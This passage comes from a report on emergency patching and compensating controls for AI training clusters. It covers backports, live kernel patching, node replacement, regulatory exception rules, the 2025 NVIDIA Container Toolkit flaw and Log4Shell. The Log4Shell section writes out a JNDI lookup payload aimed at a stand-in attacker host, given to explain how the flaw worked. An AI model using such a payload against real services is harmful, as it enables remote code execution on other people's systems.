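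Vendors sell backporting as a service. In *The Hidden Cost of Forced Upgrades*, Amaral (2026) claims that an organization with dozens of services can save thousands of engineering hours a year by backporting instead of upgrading. Amaral gives no data for the claim and is a co-founder of Root, which automates backports.

### Making a backport

Suppose the cluster runs version 7.3.0 of its login gateway and the fix is in 7.3.6. An engineer searches the maintainers' repository for the commit that fixed the flaw and any later commits that correct the fix. They also check whether 7.3.0 has the flaw, since the faulty code may have been added in a later version.

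Next, the engineer tries to apply the commit unchanged with a standard tool such as git. If the surrounding code has changed too much, the tool rejects the patch and the engineer has to adapt it. *PortGPT* (2025), a paper on automating this work, describes how a human expert handled one such case, a kernel memory flaw (CVE-2022-32250). The fix moved a safety check earlier by editing two functions, and neither edit applied to the older 5.4 series. In the first function, the expert found from the project's history that a variable had a different name in the old version, and changed the patch to match. The second function didn't exist in 5.4. Its code was part of another function in a different file, so the expert made the edit there.

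To show that the flaw is gone, the engineer runs a known attack against the unpatched program, where it should succeed, and then against the patched one, where it should fail. Without the first run, a failed attack may only mean that the attack code was broken. The engineer also runs the program's existing tests on both copies to look for changes in behavior. The attack test isn't always possible. More than a quarter of the kernel bugs in *From Finding to Deployment* had no program that could trigger them.

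Finally, the internal build system compiles and signs the result and gives it a distinct version number, such as 7.3.0+fix1. The record should give the CVE number, the original commit, the reason for each adaptation and the names of the two people who approved it. The pin moves to 7.3.0+fix1, and every other package stays the same.

Most backports need little adaptation. *BackportBench* (Zhong, Huang and He, 2025) examined 619 backports from Python, Java and JavaScript packages. Maintainers reused the original patch unchanged in 48% of cases and only moved it to a different place in another 26%. About 22% needed new logic or structure. Where both patches edited the same files, at least three quarters of the unchanged backports appeared on the same day as the original, but a quarter of those needing structural changes took four days or more. An operator with a three-day deadline would have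 had to write those slower backports in-house. The sample covers only backports that maintainers chose to make, and they probably skipped many of the harder ones.

### Distributions and long-term branches

For the operating system, the cluster's Linux distribution usually does this work. The kernel project also maintains long-term support branches, which receive fixes for years but few new features. According to *PatchNet* (2019), a fix for these branches must enter the main kernel first, contain fewer than 100 lines and be obviously correct. Developers tag suitable fixes, and the branch maintainers add them.

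In April 2026, for example, Debian 12's OpenSSH package was still based on version 9.2p1, from early 2023. Debian's comparison of two package versions lists 45 patches on top of the original source. Eleven have CVE numbers in their names and cover eight flaws. The list also includes the two-line change from July 2024, and many of the other patches adapt the program to Debian's conventions. The full version number went from 9.2p1-2+deb12u8 to 9.2p1-2+deb12u9, so an administrator who looks only at "9.2p1" would see no change.

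Debian's largest addition to OpenSSH is a patch of about 2,800 lines for GSS-API, a login method that organizations often use with a central identity server. The April update fixed a flaw in that patch, CVE-2026-3497. A cluster that compiled OpenSSH's own source without the patch would not have had the flaw. Distribution packages save operators a lot of work, but operators also need to review the extra code.

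Maintainers also miss fixes. *An Investigation of Patch Porting Practices of the Linux Kernel Ecosystem* (2024) compared which patches distributions and the kernel's long-term branches had adopted. About 30% of the patches that distributions had adopted but the long-term branches had missed might have been needed in those branches too. A cluster's staff should therefore watch the security notices of at least one other distribution, even if they install nothing from it.

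### Patching a dependency yourself

GitLab's *How to handle upstream security patches* covers cases where a library's maintainers have no fix ready or have abandoned the library. If the official fix won't arrive before the deadline, or the flaw has the highest severity, GitLab's developers write a "monkey patch", which replaces the faulty function from outside the library while the program runs. If that is impractical, they copy the library into their own fork. They also open a task to remove the workaround and make it due when they expect the official fix.

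Maintaining a fork can take a lot of work. Each time the original library gets a security fix, someone has to check whether the fork needs it and adapt it if so. *MigGPT*, a paper about kernel patches that companies and projects keep outside the main kernel, says carrying them to new kernel versions takes significant effort from experienced engineers. With a due date like GitLab's, someone at least has to ask whether the fork is still necessary.

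A library that another dependency brings in is harder to replace. If a web framework requires version 4.2.1 of an image decoder and the team has built a fixed copy, npm's `overrides`, Go's `replace` and uv's `override-dependencies` let the team choose a version regardless of that requirement. Cargo's `[patch]` can also substitute the fixed copy, but only if its version is compatible. pip, Python's standard installer, has no override, but a backport often satisfies a strict requirement anyway because Python's version rules treat `4.2.1+fix1` as a match for `4.2.1`. Overriding to a much newer release is riskier because the framework's developers may never have tested with it.

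pnpm, Yarn and Bun can instead store a small patch file and reapply it at every installation. This is easy to review and to remove later. But an inventory that a tool generates from the lockfile may still list the unpatched version, so the team has to record the patch separately.

### AI-written backports

For an automated tool, backporting a known fix is easier than writing one from scratch. *PortGPT* gave GPT-4o, an OpenAI model from 2024, tools to search the code and its history, compile the result and try again after errors. The system succeeded on 89% of 1,815 cases from older datasets and 62% of 146 harder ones. It also backported 9 of 18 recent fixes to the Linux 6.1 branch, and the kernel's maintainers merged all nine.

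The success of automated backporting depends heavily on how much of the patch has to change. *Benchmarking Automated Security Patch Backporting* (Yang, Zhang and colleagues, 2026) tested four tools on 634 newer cases in C and C++, and PortGPT did best. The middle column below comes from Zhong and colleagues' sample of packages in other languages, so it gives only a rough idea of how common each kind of change is.

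| Adaptation needed | Share of the 619 backports | PortGPT's success rate in C and C++ |
|---|---|---|
| None | 48% | 85.2% |
| New location only | 26% | 74.4% |
| New names | 4% | 49.4% |
| New logic or structure | 22% | 24.0% |

Git can apply most patches in the first row without AI, so a team should try Git first. Each attempt by PortGPT took about two minutes and cost 38 cents on average, so discarding a bad one wastes little time or money. No tool succeeded on a patch of more than 500 changed lines.

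Partial fixes are the failures that worry a security team most. Yang and colleagues studied 120 failed attempts at the two harder kinds of backport. In 45%, the patch was malformed, in the wrong place or mixed with unrelated edits, which a reviewer would probably notice. In another 39%, the fix needed coordinated changes in several places and the tool made only some of them. For one kernel change, PortGPT produced two edits in header files but left out all eight edits to the code that used them.

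The researchers also tested PortGPT on 45 cases that had both a working attack and the developers' tests. Its patch blocked the attack and passed the tests in 36 of them. When the researchers gave it the test results and had it try again, the total rose to only 37.

Zhong and colleagues got better results on structural changes with a general coding agent. Their best combination used Claude Sonnet 4, from 2025, and solved 20 of 32 such cases. It solved 71% of all 202 tasks, with rates of 91% for Python and under 50% for Java and JavaScript.

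All these models are now old, and current ones would probably do considerably better. *SoK: Assessing the Evolution of LLM Capability in Software Vulnerability Research* (2026) concludes that by November 2026, AI agents had found, validated and patched real flaws without human help, and had checked their own patches. An operator can reasonably let a current model draft the backport. The draft still needs the same human review and before-and-after attack test as any other backport, but people can read a small patch quickly.

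### Fixes that are incomplete or hard to see

If a fix is incomplete, an exact backport of it will be too. CVE-2015-9289 was a memory flaw in the kernel's drivers for digital TV receivers. According to *Characteristics, Root Causes, and Detection of Incomplete Security Bug Fixes* (2025), its fix left the same mistake in several related drivers. The maintainers later corrected those drivers in an ordinary bug fix without a new CVE number. A team that searches only for CVE numbers would backport the first fix and miss the second.

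*Beyond the Patch* (2026) found a similar gap in PraisonAI, a framework for building AI agents. A fix stopped the framework from loading untrusted local code through one function but left another route open, which the developers closed only in version 4.6.32. The advisory for the original flaw also listed 4.5.139 as the fixed version, although the new check first appears in 4.5.140. A cluster that fast-tracked 4.5.139 would have remained vulnerable to the original flaw. Comparing the release with the source repository should reveal the missing check, but reviewers also have to search the rest of the program for the same mistake.

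Red Hat's *Backporting Security Fixes* warns that scanners relying on version numbers raise false alarms about backported packages. Another Red Hat article, *determining your risk*, adds that these scanners can miss real flaws.

An administrator can instead search the package's changelog for the CVE number, as Plixer's *Check vulnerabilities* recommends. This fails if the changelog doesn't include the number. The entry for Debian's two-line OpenSSH patch, as Martin quoted it the day after release, mentioned only the return of a 2006 flaw, so a search for the new number, CVE-2024-6387, would not have matched it. For its own backports, the team has to publish an internal VEX statement, since no outside database lists 7.3.0+fix1.

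### Live patching the kernel

A new kernel normally takes effect only after a reboot, which can stop a large training job. Kernel live patching avoids this by correcting a function while the machine keeps running. (Java programs allow something similar, which defenders used against Log4Shell in 2021.)

The Linux kernel documentation's *Livepatch* explains how to correct a faulty function in a running kernel. The compiler leaves a small hook, originally meant for tracing tools, at the start of most kernel functions. A live patch is a kernel module that contains a corrected copy of the faulty function. After an administrator loads it, each call to the old function reaches the hook first, and the kernel redirects the call to the new copy before the old code touches any data.

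Some fixes change several functions together, for example to change the order in which they lock shared data. A program that used the old version of one function and the new version of another could hang. Linux avoids this by switching each task to the new versions separately. It switches a sleeping task if the task is not in the middle of an affected function. Other tasks switch when they return from the kernel to their own code.

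The transition usually takes a few seconds, but a task stuck inside an old function can delay it indefinitely. Every 15 seconds, the kernel prompts such tasks to switch. An administrator can also force the switch, but the documentation advises planning a reboot afterwards and not applying any more live patches until then. Loading the patch doesn't prove that every task is using it, so operators have to check that the transition has finished on every machine.

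Live patches can't deliver every fix. The kernel can't redirect functions that lack the hook that live patching relies on, including parts of the live-patching code itself. *The Case for DBMS Live Patching* (2024) notes that Kpatch, a common tool for building live patches, works only on programs written in C and replaces whole functions. Adding a field to data already in memory is difficult because existing records don't have the field. A fix to code that runs only at startup has no effect until the next startup.

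Live patching also involves a security trade-off. *Neverland* (2019) proposes hardware that locks the kernel's code so that an intruder can't alter it. The lock also blocks live patches, so a machine with the full protection has to reboot for every kernel fix. A cluster that allows live patches should at least accept only modules signed with its internal key.

A live patch disappears at the next reboot, so the team must also install the corrected kernel on disk. Until that reboot, the machine's memory stays intact, which helps if the operators still have to look for signs of a break-in.

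*Runtime Software Patching* (2022) describes a more ambitious method, which saves the state of running programs, starts a new kernel and then restores the programs. It can handle all kinds of kernel fix, but testing it takes a lot of work. On a training machine, it would also have to save and restore the accelerators' state.

### Replacing machines between checkpoints

If a fix needs a reboot, the operators can wait until the training job has saved a checkpoint, a copy of its state that it can resume from. In a rolling replacement, they patch some spare machines, swap them into the job at a checkpoint, then patch the machines they took out and repeat.

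Suppose a job uses 960 machines with eight chips each, and the cluster has 40 spares. The job saves a checkpoint every hour and needs ten minutes to restart after a swap. Replacing all 960 machines takes 24 swaps over about a day, and the job loses four hours of training time. If the operators instead stop the job after a checkpoint, reboot all the machines at once in 30 minutes and restart, the job loses 40 minutes, or 5,120 chip-hours.

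For one large job, rolling replacement can waste six times as much computing time as a single stop. It works better when the cluster runs many small jobs, since the others can continue while one stops. It also wastes little time if operators make the replacements during restarts that hardware failures would have caused anyway. But an attacker may need only one unpatched machine, so the cluster stays exposed until the last one is patched.

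A mixed plan makes more sense for an urgent fix. The operators swap in the 40 patched spares at one checkpoint, watch them for a few hours, then reboot the other machines together at a later checkpoint. In the example, they lose 50 minutes of training and still catch most faulty kernels before they reach the whole cluster. The 40 machines they swapped out then serve as spares. If 2% of the remaining 920 don't come back after the reboot, the spares can replace those 18 or so machines.

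### Closed drivers and firmware

An operator can't backport a fix to a closed GPU driver whose source code it doesn't have, or to firmware that only the manufacturer can sign. Reviewers can check the signature on the vendor's update and test how it behaves, but they have to trust the vendor's account of what it does.

Operators can best prepare by choosing a branch that the vendor promises to maintain. NVIDIA says it supports each production branch of its main AI tools and frameworks for nine months, with regular security updates and no changes to the interfaces that applications use. It also offers a long-term branch for a smaller set of tools, including stable versions of infrastructure software such as drivers. A cluster already on such a branch can take a relatively small update in an emergency, while one on an unsupported driver may first have to upgrade to a different branch. Until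 the vendor releases a fix, operators can only restrict who and what can reach the flawed driver.

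## Protecting a cluster that cannot yet be patched

Operators sometimes have to keep running a flawed program past its patching deadline. The vendor may not have released a fix, reviewers may have found a change they can't explain, or the fix may crash training jobs in staging. The operators then need an emergency exception to keep the old version, and compensating controls to block or limit exploitation of the flaw until they can install the fix.

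The US Department of Defense's *DoD Vulnerability Management* (2020) separates remediation, which removes a vulnerability, from mitigation, which reduces its impact but leaves it in place. Compensating controls are mitigation. An effective control ends the exposure window, but flaw-days keep adding up because the flawed code is still on the machine.

### Interrupting the attack

Suppose version 4.2.1 of the image decoder mishandles a rare image format, so a malformed file can run an attacker's code on the machine that opens it. The fix in 4.2.2 has failed in staging. To steal data, the attacker has to get a file to the decoder, trigger the faulty code, use the decoder's access to reach the data, and send it out. Operators can interfere with each of these steps.

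The best option is usually to switch off the flawed feature, in this case support for the rare format, so that the attack fails however the attacker disguises the file. NERC's *CIP-007-6*, the patching standard for the North American power grid, notes that disabling a service can also protect against several flaws at once. But a setting may not cover every route to the flawed code, which is why the first recommended Log4j settings failed in 2021. Some programs also read their settings only at startup, and a machine rebuilt from an old gold image will have the feature back on. Switching off a feature can also create a different problem. In 2024, administrators could block an attack on OpenSSH by turning off its login timer, but this made it easier for an attacker to tie up the server with unfinished logins.

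If researchers need the format, operators can allow only a few machines to send files to the decoder. This does not stop a malicious user on a permitted machine or an intruder who has taken one over. It also fails if operators overlook another path to the decoder. For example, a firewall rule on the main network does not block files that arrive through shared storage.

Filtering rejects files that look like the attack and lets the rest through. It is popular because it disturbs users least, but it is also the easiest control to get around. A filter that looks for a known malicious pattern will miss a file that triggers the same fault in a different way, and it can't inspect encrypted traffic. Converting every incoming image to a simple format on a disposable machine is safer because it doesn't depend on recognizing the attack. The converter should not use the same flawed decoder, since it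 will be handling hostile files.

The next control is to run the decoder under an account that can't read model weights, passwords or other users' files, so that an attacker who takes it over gains little. A second flaw can undo this, as the kernel exploit did in Dream's PHP campaign. A more ordinary cause of failure is a forgotten credential, such as an access key left in a configuration file, which may give the decoder's account far more access than its permissions do.

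Blocking outbound traffic prevents the attacker's code from fetching more tools, receiving commands or sending data out. It doesn't prevent sabotage, since code that corrupts a training run needs no outside connection. Attackers can also hide data in traffic that operators have to allow, such as name lookups or the result files researchers export.

Closer monitoring doesn't prevent an attack, but it can shorten the time an intruder has. It fails if the intruder can erase the logs or if nobody reads the alerts. For the most important grid systems, NERC requires companies to review at least a summary or sample of logged events every 15 days. That is much too infrequent for a machine with a known flaw, whose logs somebody should read daily.

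Operators can test all six controls without waiting for an attacker:

| Control | Test for the image decoder | Repeat the test after |
|---|---|---|
| Switch off the format | Submit a harmless file in that format to every service that uses the decoder | Any restart or rebuild |
| Block the path | Try to submit a file from each part of the network that has lost access | Any network or storage change |
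| Filter the input | Send known attack files and altered copies through the filter | Each newly published attack |
| Remove privileges | Run a harmless program under the decoder's account and try to read weights and passwords | Any change to accounts |
| Block outbound traffic | Try to send a marked file out by every protocol the machine supports | Any new export route |
| Monitor more closely | Trigger a harmless alert on a Saturday night and time the response | Any change to logging or the rota |

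As with a backport, the team should run the first five tests before and after turning the control on. It should also check that ordinary work still gets through, because people tend to turn off a control that gets in their way.

Combining controls helps, but less than multiplying their failure rates would imply, because controls often fail together. Three controls that each stop 90% of attempts would let through only one attempt in a thousand if they failed independently, but an intruder with a stolen administrator account may be able to switch off all three.

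### How often interim measures fail

Known failures such as the Log4j settings show how interim measures break down, but they don't give a failure rate. Calculating one would also require counting the measures that held. The Department of Defense tells its organizations to keep statistics on patching, such as the mean time to patch, the success rate of deployments and the average exposure. None of these examples counts the mitigations that attackers bypassed.

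A team can measure its own controls, although small tests prove little. Suppose the filter blocks all n of the attack variants that the team tries. The highest bypass rate that is still consistent with this result, at 95% confidence, is:

$$p = 1 - 0.05^{1/n}$$

For 20 variants this is about 14%, and for 100 variants about 3%. Even these figures are optimistic, because they assume that the variants are a random sample of what attackers would send, whereas real attackers keep adjusting a file until a version gets through. The formula also doesn't help in assessing a control such as switching off a feature, which depends on whether the team has found every route to the code.

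### The payment card rules

The most detailed public test for a compensating control is in the PCI Security Standards Council's *Payment Card Industry Data Security Standard* (PCI DSS, 2024), which companies that handle payment cards have to follow. The council asked for comments on version 4.0.1 in June 2026, but that version was still current when Malone wrote *Mapping PCI DSS v4.0.1 to the NIST Cybersecurity Framework 2.0* in July 2026.

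A company can use a compensating control only if a documented technical or business constraint prevents it from meeting a requirement. The control must:

- "Meet the intent and rigor of the original PCI DSS requirement"
- provide "a similar level of defense"
- be "above and beyond" the other PCI DSS requirements
- address the additional risk of not meeting the requirement
- address the requirement "currently and in the future", so it can't excuse a task that the company skipped two quarters ago.

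"Above and beyond" means that a company can't count a measure it already had to take for the same item. For example, locking users out after several wrong passwords can't make up for sending passwords unencrypted, because lockout is already a separate requirement and doesn't prevent anyone from intercepting a password.

The standard's example is a flaw that attackers can exploit over a network and for which the vendor has released no update. The company can divide its internal network into segments, let only the necessary devices reach the flawed interface, and monitor all traffic to it. These measures all apply to the network path to the flaw, so they wouldn't stop an attacker on a permitted device, though the monitoring might reveal the attack. A cluster that holds weights should add a control that limits what an attacker can do after exploiting the flaw, such as removing the flawed program's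 privileges.

The company fills in a worksheet with the constraint, the control, the objective, the remaining risk, and how it tested the control and will maintain it. An assessor checks the control every year. The PCI Security Standards Council's newer guidance, *PCI SSC Publishes New Guidance on Compensating Controls and the Customized Approach*, adds that an assessor who helped design or implement a control may not also assess it.

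*All About INFI*, a set of slides by two of the council's managers, O'Connor and Bloomfield, rules out poor planning as a reason for a compensating control. For a cluster, the lack of a vendor fix would be a valid constraint, but a shortage of weekend reviewers would probably count as poor planning.

### The power grid's 35-day cycle

CIP-007-6 gives grid companies more freedom. At least every 35 days, a company has to check which newly released security patches apply to its systems. It then has another 35 days to install each applicable patch, write a dated mitigation plan or revise an existing plan. If a patch comes out the day after a check, the company could take almost 70 days to do any of these. An attacker who began exploiting the flaw five days after the patch came out, Mandiant's average for 2023, would by then have been exploiting it for about two months.

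The plan must include the company's "planned actions to mitigate the vulnerabilities" and "a timeframe to complete these mitigations". A company asked Alrich (2017), who writes about grid security, whether it could just explain the delay and promise a later installation date. An auditor he consulted said the plan must document when and how the company will address the vulnerability.

The date can be tied to an event instead of a calendar day. NERC accepts wording such as "at next scheduled outage of at least two days duration", and according to its guidance there is no maximum timeframe. Patching carries its own risk to the grid, and a company may have to put off changes during a storm or a period of high demand. If the company can't meet its date, a designated senior manager or a delegate has to approve an extension.

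This flexibility makes sense for a power station, but an AI company that copied it would leave a large gap. If a plan lists only steps already taken, it counts as implemented once the paperwork is complete. A company could therefore disable a service, record this in its plan and never install the patch. The rule also applies only once a patch is released, as ReliabilityFirst's *Patch Management Mitigation Plans* (2018) notes, so a publicly known flaw without a patch needs no plan. ReliabilityFirst, one of the grid's regional regulators, advises companies to track those flaws anyway.

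In March 2026 the US energy regulator FERC approved a package of grid standards that includes a new version of CIP-007, CIP-007-7.1, which will take effect in 2028, according to Troutman Energy Report's *FERC Approves Virtualization CIP Reliability Standards and Definitions* (2026). Companies can adopt it earlier. NERC's *CIP-007-7*, which NERC later corrected to become 7.1, keeps both 35-day periods and the dated plan.

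FERC did object to another change in the package. Under the old rules, a company that was technically unable to meet certain requirements had to apply for an exception and use measures that "achieve at least a comparable level of security". The new standards let companies decide for themselves that a system can't meet a requirement, without reporting it. FERC's *Virtualization Reliability Standards* (2026) approved the standards but ordered NERC to write clear criteria, make companies report these exceptions and report combined figures to FERC every year. The patching requirement doesn't include the self-granted exception, but FERC's worry applies to any cluster whose operators approve their own delays, so someone outside the operations team should see every exception.

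### Defence plans of action

The US military requires its organizations to report mitigations and accepted risks to the headquarters that defends its networks. US Cyber Command can order a particular fix or mitigation, and can disconnect a system from the network. The Department of Defense confirms that a fix has worked by comparing successive vulnerability scans. Scans are less useful for checking a compensating control, because a scanner that reads version numbers will report the flaw whether or not the control works. Checking the control would require the tests in the table above.

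Defence offices often record unfinished security work in a "plan of action and milestones", which lists each weakness with the steps and dates for addressing it. *DODIG-2023-057* (2023), from the Pentagon's inspector general, recommended that one of the department's IT providers set a time limit for mitigating every vulnerability and write such a plan for any it couldn't mitigate in time.

Under CMMC, the programme that certifies contractors' security, a company that fails some requirements can hold a conditional status for at most 180 days, according to a final rule in the Federal Register (2025). The Code of Federal Regulations' *Plan of Action and Milestones requirements* allows this only for selected requirements. The 180-day limit is a deadline for closing gaps that an assessment found and doesn't give a company 180 days to install each patch.

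Patches normally belong in a separate "operational plan of action". As defined in Coalfire Federal's *CFR 32 Digest* (2024), this plan covers temporary vulnerabilities and deficiencies, including necessary updates and patches. GuidePoint Security's *Understanding CMMC* says a temporary deficiency has no standard duration.

None of these rules sets a fixed limit on how long a control may stand in for a missing patch, so a cluster's operators have to choose one. A reasonable exception would expire after 14 days, or earlier if the control fails a test or somebody publishes a new way to exploit the flaw. Renewing it would require fresh test results and approval from someone who didn't design the control. If the vendor takes three months to release a fix, the team would have to defend the decision about six times, which takes some work but makes the flaw much harder to forget.

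### The NVIDIA flaw of 2025

The NVIDIA Container Toolkit lets programs in containers use the GPUs of the machine they run on. Nearly every shared GPU cluster needs something like it. In July 2025 the security company Wiz disclosed a flaw in the toolkit, CVE-2025-23266, that let a malicious container take full control of its host. Wiz rated its severity 9.0 out of 10.

When a container starts, the toolkit prepares the GPU for it by running small programs called hooks, which run outside the container with high privileges. Zero Day Initiative's *(Pwn2Own) NVIDIA Container Toolkit Environment Variable Handling Local Privilege Escalation Vulnerability* (2025) traces the flaw to missing restrictions on environment variables, settings that a program receives when it starts. A malicious container image could supply settings that made a privileged hook run the attacker's code.

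NVIDIA fixed the flaw in version 1.17.8 of the toolkit and version 25.3.1 of the GPU Operator, which installs the toolkit on clusters. TechRepublic's *Critical Flaw in NVIDIA AI Toolkit Puts Cloud Services at Risk* reports that NVIDIA advised anyone who couldn't update at once to disable the `enable-cuda-compat` hook. Administrators do this by setting `disable-cuda-compat-lib-hook` to true in the toolkit's configuration file. Red Hat's *CVE-2025-23267* gives this setting for a companion flaw in the same hook and says it applies to the toolkit's legacy mode. On clusters that use the GPU Operator, administrators can disable the hook through the deployment settings instead, according to BeyondMachines' *NVIDIA reports container escape vulnerabilities in Container Toolkit*.

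The hook helps a container use newer CUDA libraries (NVIDIA's software for running programs on GPUs) than the host's driver normally supports. Clusters with pinned drivers are the most likely to need it. If the driver is a year old and researchers bring in containers with current libraries, some of their jobs may fail once the hook is off. The team would have to find those jobs and rebuild their containers with older libraries, or review the fixed toolkit faster.

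NVIDIA recommended the setting, but Red Hat's *CVE-2025-23266* says that no available mitigation met Red Hat's criteria. Red Hat's AI product was not affected because it used a newer toolkit in a different mode, called CDI, and didn't rely on the hook. BeyondMachines reports that in CDI mode, only toolkit versions before 1.17.5 had the flaw. An operator therefore has to check both the version and the mode before deciding that a node is safe or that the setting will protect it.

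Suppose a cluster has 200 shared GPU nodes that run version 1.17.6 in legacy mode. The operators can change the setting on every node within hours, while reviewers work on 1.17.8. To check the change, they start a harmless container on each node and confirm that the hook no longer appears in its startup configuration. They can also run a known attack, with the hook on and then off, on a spare node that has no access to the rest of the cluster. They should add the setting to the gold image as well, or rebuilt nodes will be vulnerable again.

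The hook runs only when a container starts, so the new setting can't undo an earlier escape. If somebody ran an untrusted container on a node before the change, the team should check that node for a break-in before trusting it again.

The setting closes one way out of the container, and these further controls would limit the damage if an attacker found another:

| Control | On the GPU nodes | What remains exposed |
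|---|---|---|
| Block the path | Start only container images that the team has signed | Signed images that run code written later by users or AI agents |
| Remove privileges | Keep credentials for other systems off the nodes | Everything on the node itself |
| Separate users | Give untrusted jobs their own physical machines | Other untrusted jobs on the same machine |
| Block outbound traffic | Let nodes contact only storage and scheduling services | Data that the attacker writes to shared storage |
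| Monitor | Alert on unexpected privileged programs on the host | The time until somebody responds |

The third row matters most on a shared node. Containers on one machine use the same kernel and GPU driver, so an attacker who gains control of the host can read the memory of every job on it, including any model weights loaded there. Turning off the hook leaves the kernel and driver shared, so a flaw in either could give an attacker the same access.

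Operators also have good reason to expect more flaws of this type. *Critical NVIDIA Container Toolkit Flaw* (The Hacker News, 2025) reports that Wiz found a way around NVIDIA's fix for an earlier container escape, CVE-2024-0132. A cluster can therefore still need a second barrier after it has been patched. *Breaking Out of the AI Cage* (Ben-Sasson and Riancho, 2025) advises against using containers as the only security barrier. It recommends virtualization or safer container systems such as gVisor, which handles most of a container's requests itself instead of passing them to the host's kernel. For GPU work, gVisor still has to forward requests to NVIDIA's driver, so an attacker inside the container can still reach flaws in the driver.

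Red Hat rated the flaw "Important" instead of "Critical", partly because an attacker needs local access and some privileges inside a container. MITRE's *CVE-2025-23266* (2025) includes CISA's assessment from that July that the flaw had no known exploitation, was not automatable and had total impact. Under that assessment, the flaw gets the same deadlines as the invented container runtime flaw, which are the next upgrade under CISA's definitions and 14 or three days under the stricter ones. The stricter definitions fit a research cluster better, because every user there can start a container.

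### Isolation as a substitute for patching

Operators of air-gapped clusters may argue that the isolation is a compensating control. It does remove a lot of risk, because an outsider can't scan the cluster for flawed programs, send an exploit to one or direct an attack remotely.

Isolation also makes large thefts harder. Suppose the only way out is a link that hardware limits to one megabit per second. A terabyte of model weights would take about 93 days to copy through it, which gives defenders time to notice. But a one-megabyte file of passwords or research notes would take eight seconds.

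The air gap does little against insiders, or against anyone who has stolen a researcher's account and can enter the building. Malicious files can also get in, because the cluster has to import files to be useful. An image that exploits the decoder could arrive among millions of others in a training set. NERC requires grid companies to manage patches on standalone systems because somebody can introduce malicious code to them, deliberately or by accident, and it names Stuxnet as an example of such code. Stuxnet damaged centrifuges at an Iranian nuclear site and probably crossed the air gap on a USB drive. NVIDIA likewise told users to update its toolkit whether or not a host faced the internet, because attackers could use poisoned images or compromised repositories.

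AI agents make an air gap less useful as a substitute for patching. An agent that writes and runs code inside the cluster can reach many flaws directly, and it may follow instructions hidden in an imported document. Once it has read those instructions, it doesn't need a connection to the attacker.

An air gap around the whole cluster also does not stop an intruder from moving between its machines. Training nodes usually share storage and a fast network, and many accept commands from the same scheduler. NERC's new grid standard, *CIP-007-7*, forbids critical virtual machines from sharing processors or memory with less critical ones. A similar rule would help contain an intruder in a GPU cluster. Agents' experiments could run on different physical nodes from jobs that load the most valuable weights, with a firewall between the two groups.

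CISA's table already allows more time to patch a machine that is off the public internet, so an operator who cites the air gap to justify missing that longer deadline is counting the same protection twice. Similarly, under the payment card rule against double counting, an air gap that a cluster's security standard already requires can't also make up for a missing patch.

Isolation can still justify taking longer to patch some flaws. If a program's only flaw is that it mishandles replies from a public web server, and the cluster can't contact one, operators can reasonably leave the fix in the ordinary queue. They should record that reasoning and check it again whenever they add an import route. But everyone who could exploit a flaw in the container toolkit is already inside the cluster, so the air gap shouldn't extend the deadline for fixing it.

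## Log4Shell in December 2021

Log4Shell tested emergency patching and compensating controls at once, because the first fix and the first recommended settings both proved incomplete. It is the popular name for CVE-2021-44228, a flaw in Log4j, an open-source library that Java programs use to write logs. Volunteers maintain Log4j under the non-profit Apache Software Foundation, and developers have built it into thousands of other packages.

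### How the flaw worked

Before Log4j wrote a line to a log, it replaced expressions of the form `${...}`, called lookups, with values. This is useful in a configuration file, where `${ctx:loginId}` can add the current user's login name to every line. But Log4j also replaced lookups in the logged text itself, which may come from a stranger, as when a web service logs the name that each user types at login.

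One kind of lookup used JNDI, a Java interface for fetching data from directory servers. An attacker could type `${jndi:ldap://attacker.example/a}` as a username. When the service logged it, Log4j would contact the attacker's server over LDAP, a directory protocol, and the reply could make Java load and run the attacker's program. The attacker didn't need a password, and could put the string in any other text that the service logged.

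The US government's Cyber Safety Review Board's *Review of the December 2021 Log4j Event* (2022) traces the JNDI lookup to a patch that a member of the open-source community submitted in July 2013. Every ordinary release from 2.0-beta9 to 2.14.1 had the Log4Shell flaw. A cluster that had pinned Log4j years earlier was therefore no more exposed on 9 December 2021 than one that updated every night. Log4j 1.x, which Apache stopped supporting in 2015, was mostly unaffected because it has no lookups.

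An engineer at Alibaba Cloud privately reported the Log4j flaw to Apache on 24 November. Log4j's developers work in public, so from 29 November, 11 days before the fixed release, anyone could see their proposed changes. On 9 December a Chinese security company posted a redacted screenshot of an exploit on WeChat. The US Cyber Safety Review Board thought the company might have worked out the flaw from a release candidate published three days earlier, but couldn't confirm it. Apache brought its plans forward and released version 2.15.0 on 10 December.

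One technology company saw a spike in scanning within two hours of the disclosure, and five days later the network company Cloudflare was seeing 400 exploitation attempts per second. The board found only one trace of earlier use, on 1 and 2 December, which looked like tests of the Alibaba engineer's demonstration.

### Four releases in 18 days

Researchers looked harder at Log4j and found three more flaws that required new releases. The scores come from the Apache Software Foundation's *Apache Log4j Security Vulnerabilities*, and the CVE dates come from the board. Each release came out on or about the date of its CVE.

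| Release | CVE it fixed | Date in 2021 | What an attacker could do | Severity score |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| 2.15.0 | CVE-2021-44228 | 10 December | Run remote code through logged text | 10.0 |
| 2.16.0 | CVE-2021-45046 | 14 December | Get around the first fix in some configurations | 3.7, later 9.0 |
| 2.17.0 | CVE-2021-45105 | 18 December | Crash the program in some configurations | 5.9 |
| 2.17.1 | CVE-2021-44832 | 28 December | Run remote code after changing the logging configuration | 6.6 |

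Log4j 2.15.0 stopped replacing lookups in messages by default and tried to limit JNDI connections to the same machine. Researchers found ways around that limit. If a site's configuration used a lookup such as `${ctx:loginId}`, an attacker could put a JNDI lookup in the login name, and Log4j would still evaluate it. Version 2.16.0 removed message lookups and turned JNDI off by default.

The second flaw's score changed, which is awkward for any team that sets deadlines by severity. The Apache Software Foundation's *Apache Log4j CVEs* originally described the flaw as a way to crash a program and scored it 3.7. A reviewer who read that on the first day could reasonably have put version 2.16.0 in the ordinary queue. The score rose to 9.0 after researchers showed that attackers could steal information and run code, but the team would have had to check the rating again to learn that the patch was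 now urgent.

These version numbers are for Java 8 and later. Operators who had also pinned an older version of Java had to wait longer for a Log4j fix. On 10 December there was no fixed release for Java 7. The first was 2.12.2, which came with the second round of fixes, and the first for Java 6 was 2.3.1, which came later still. Sonatype's *Log4Shell Help for Central Publishers* (2021), a running log from the company that operates the Maven repository, announced the Java 6 and 7 versions of the fourth fix on 3 January 2022, six days after the entry for Java 8.

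### The settings that failed

Many sites could not upgrade immediately, so they configured Log4j not to process lookups in log messages. For Log4j 2.10 and later, administrators could set either `log4j2.formatMsgNoLookups` or the environment variable `LOG4J_FORMAT_MSG_NO_LOOKUPS` to true. For versions 2.7 to 2.14.1, they could add `{nolookups}` to the message pattern in the logging configuration.

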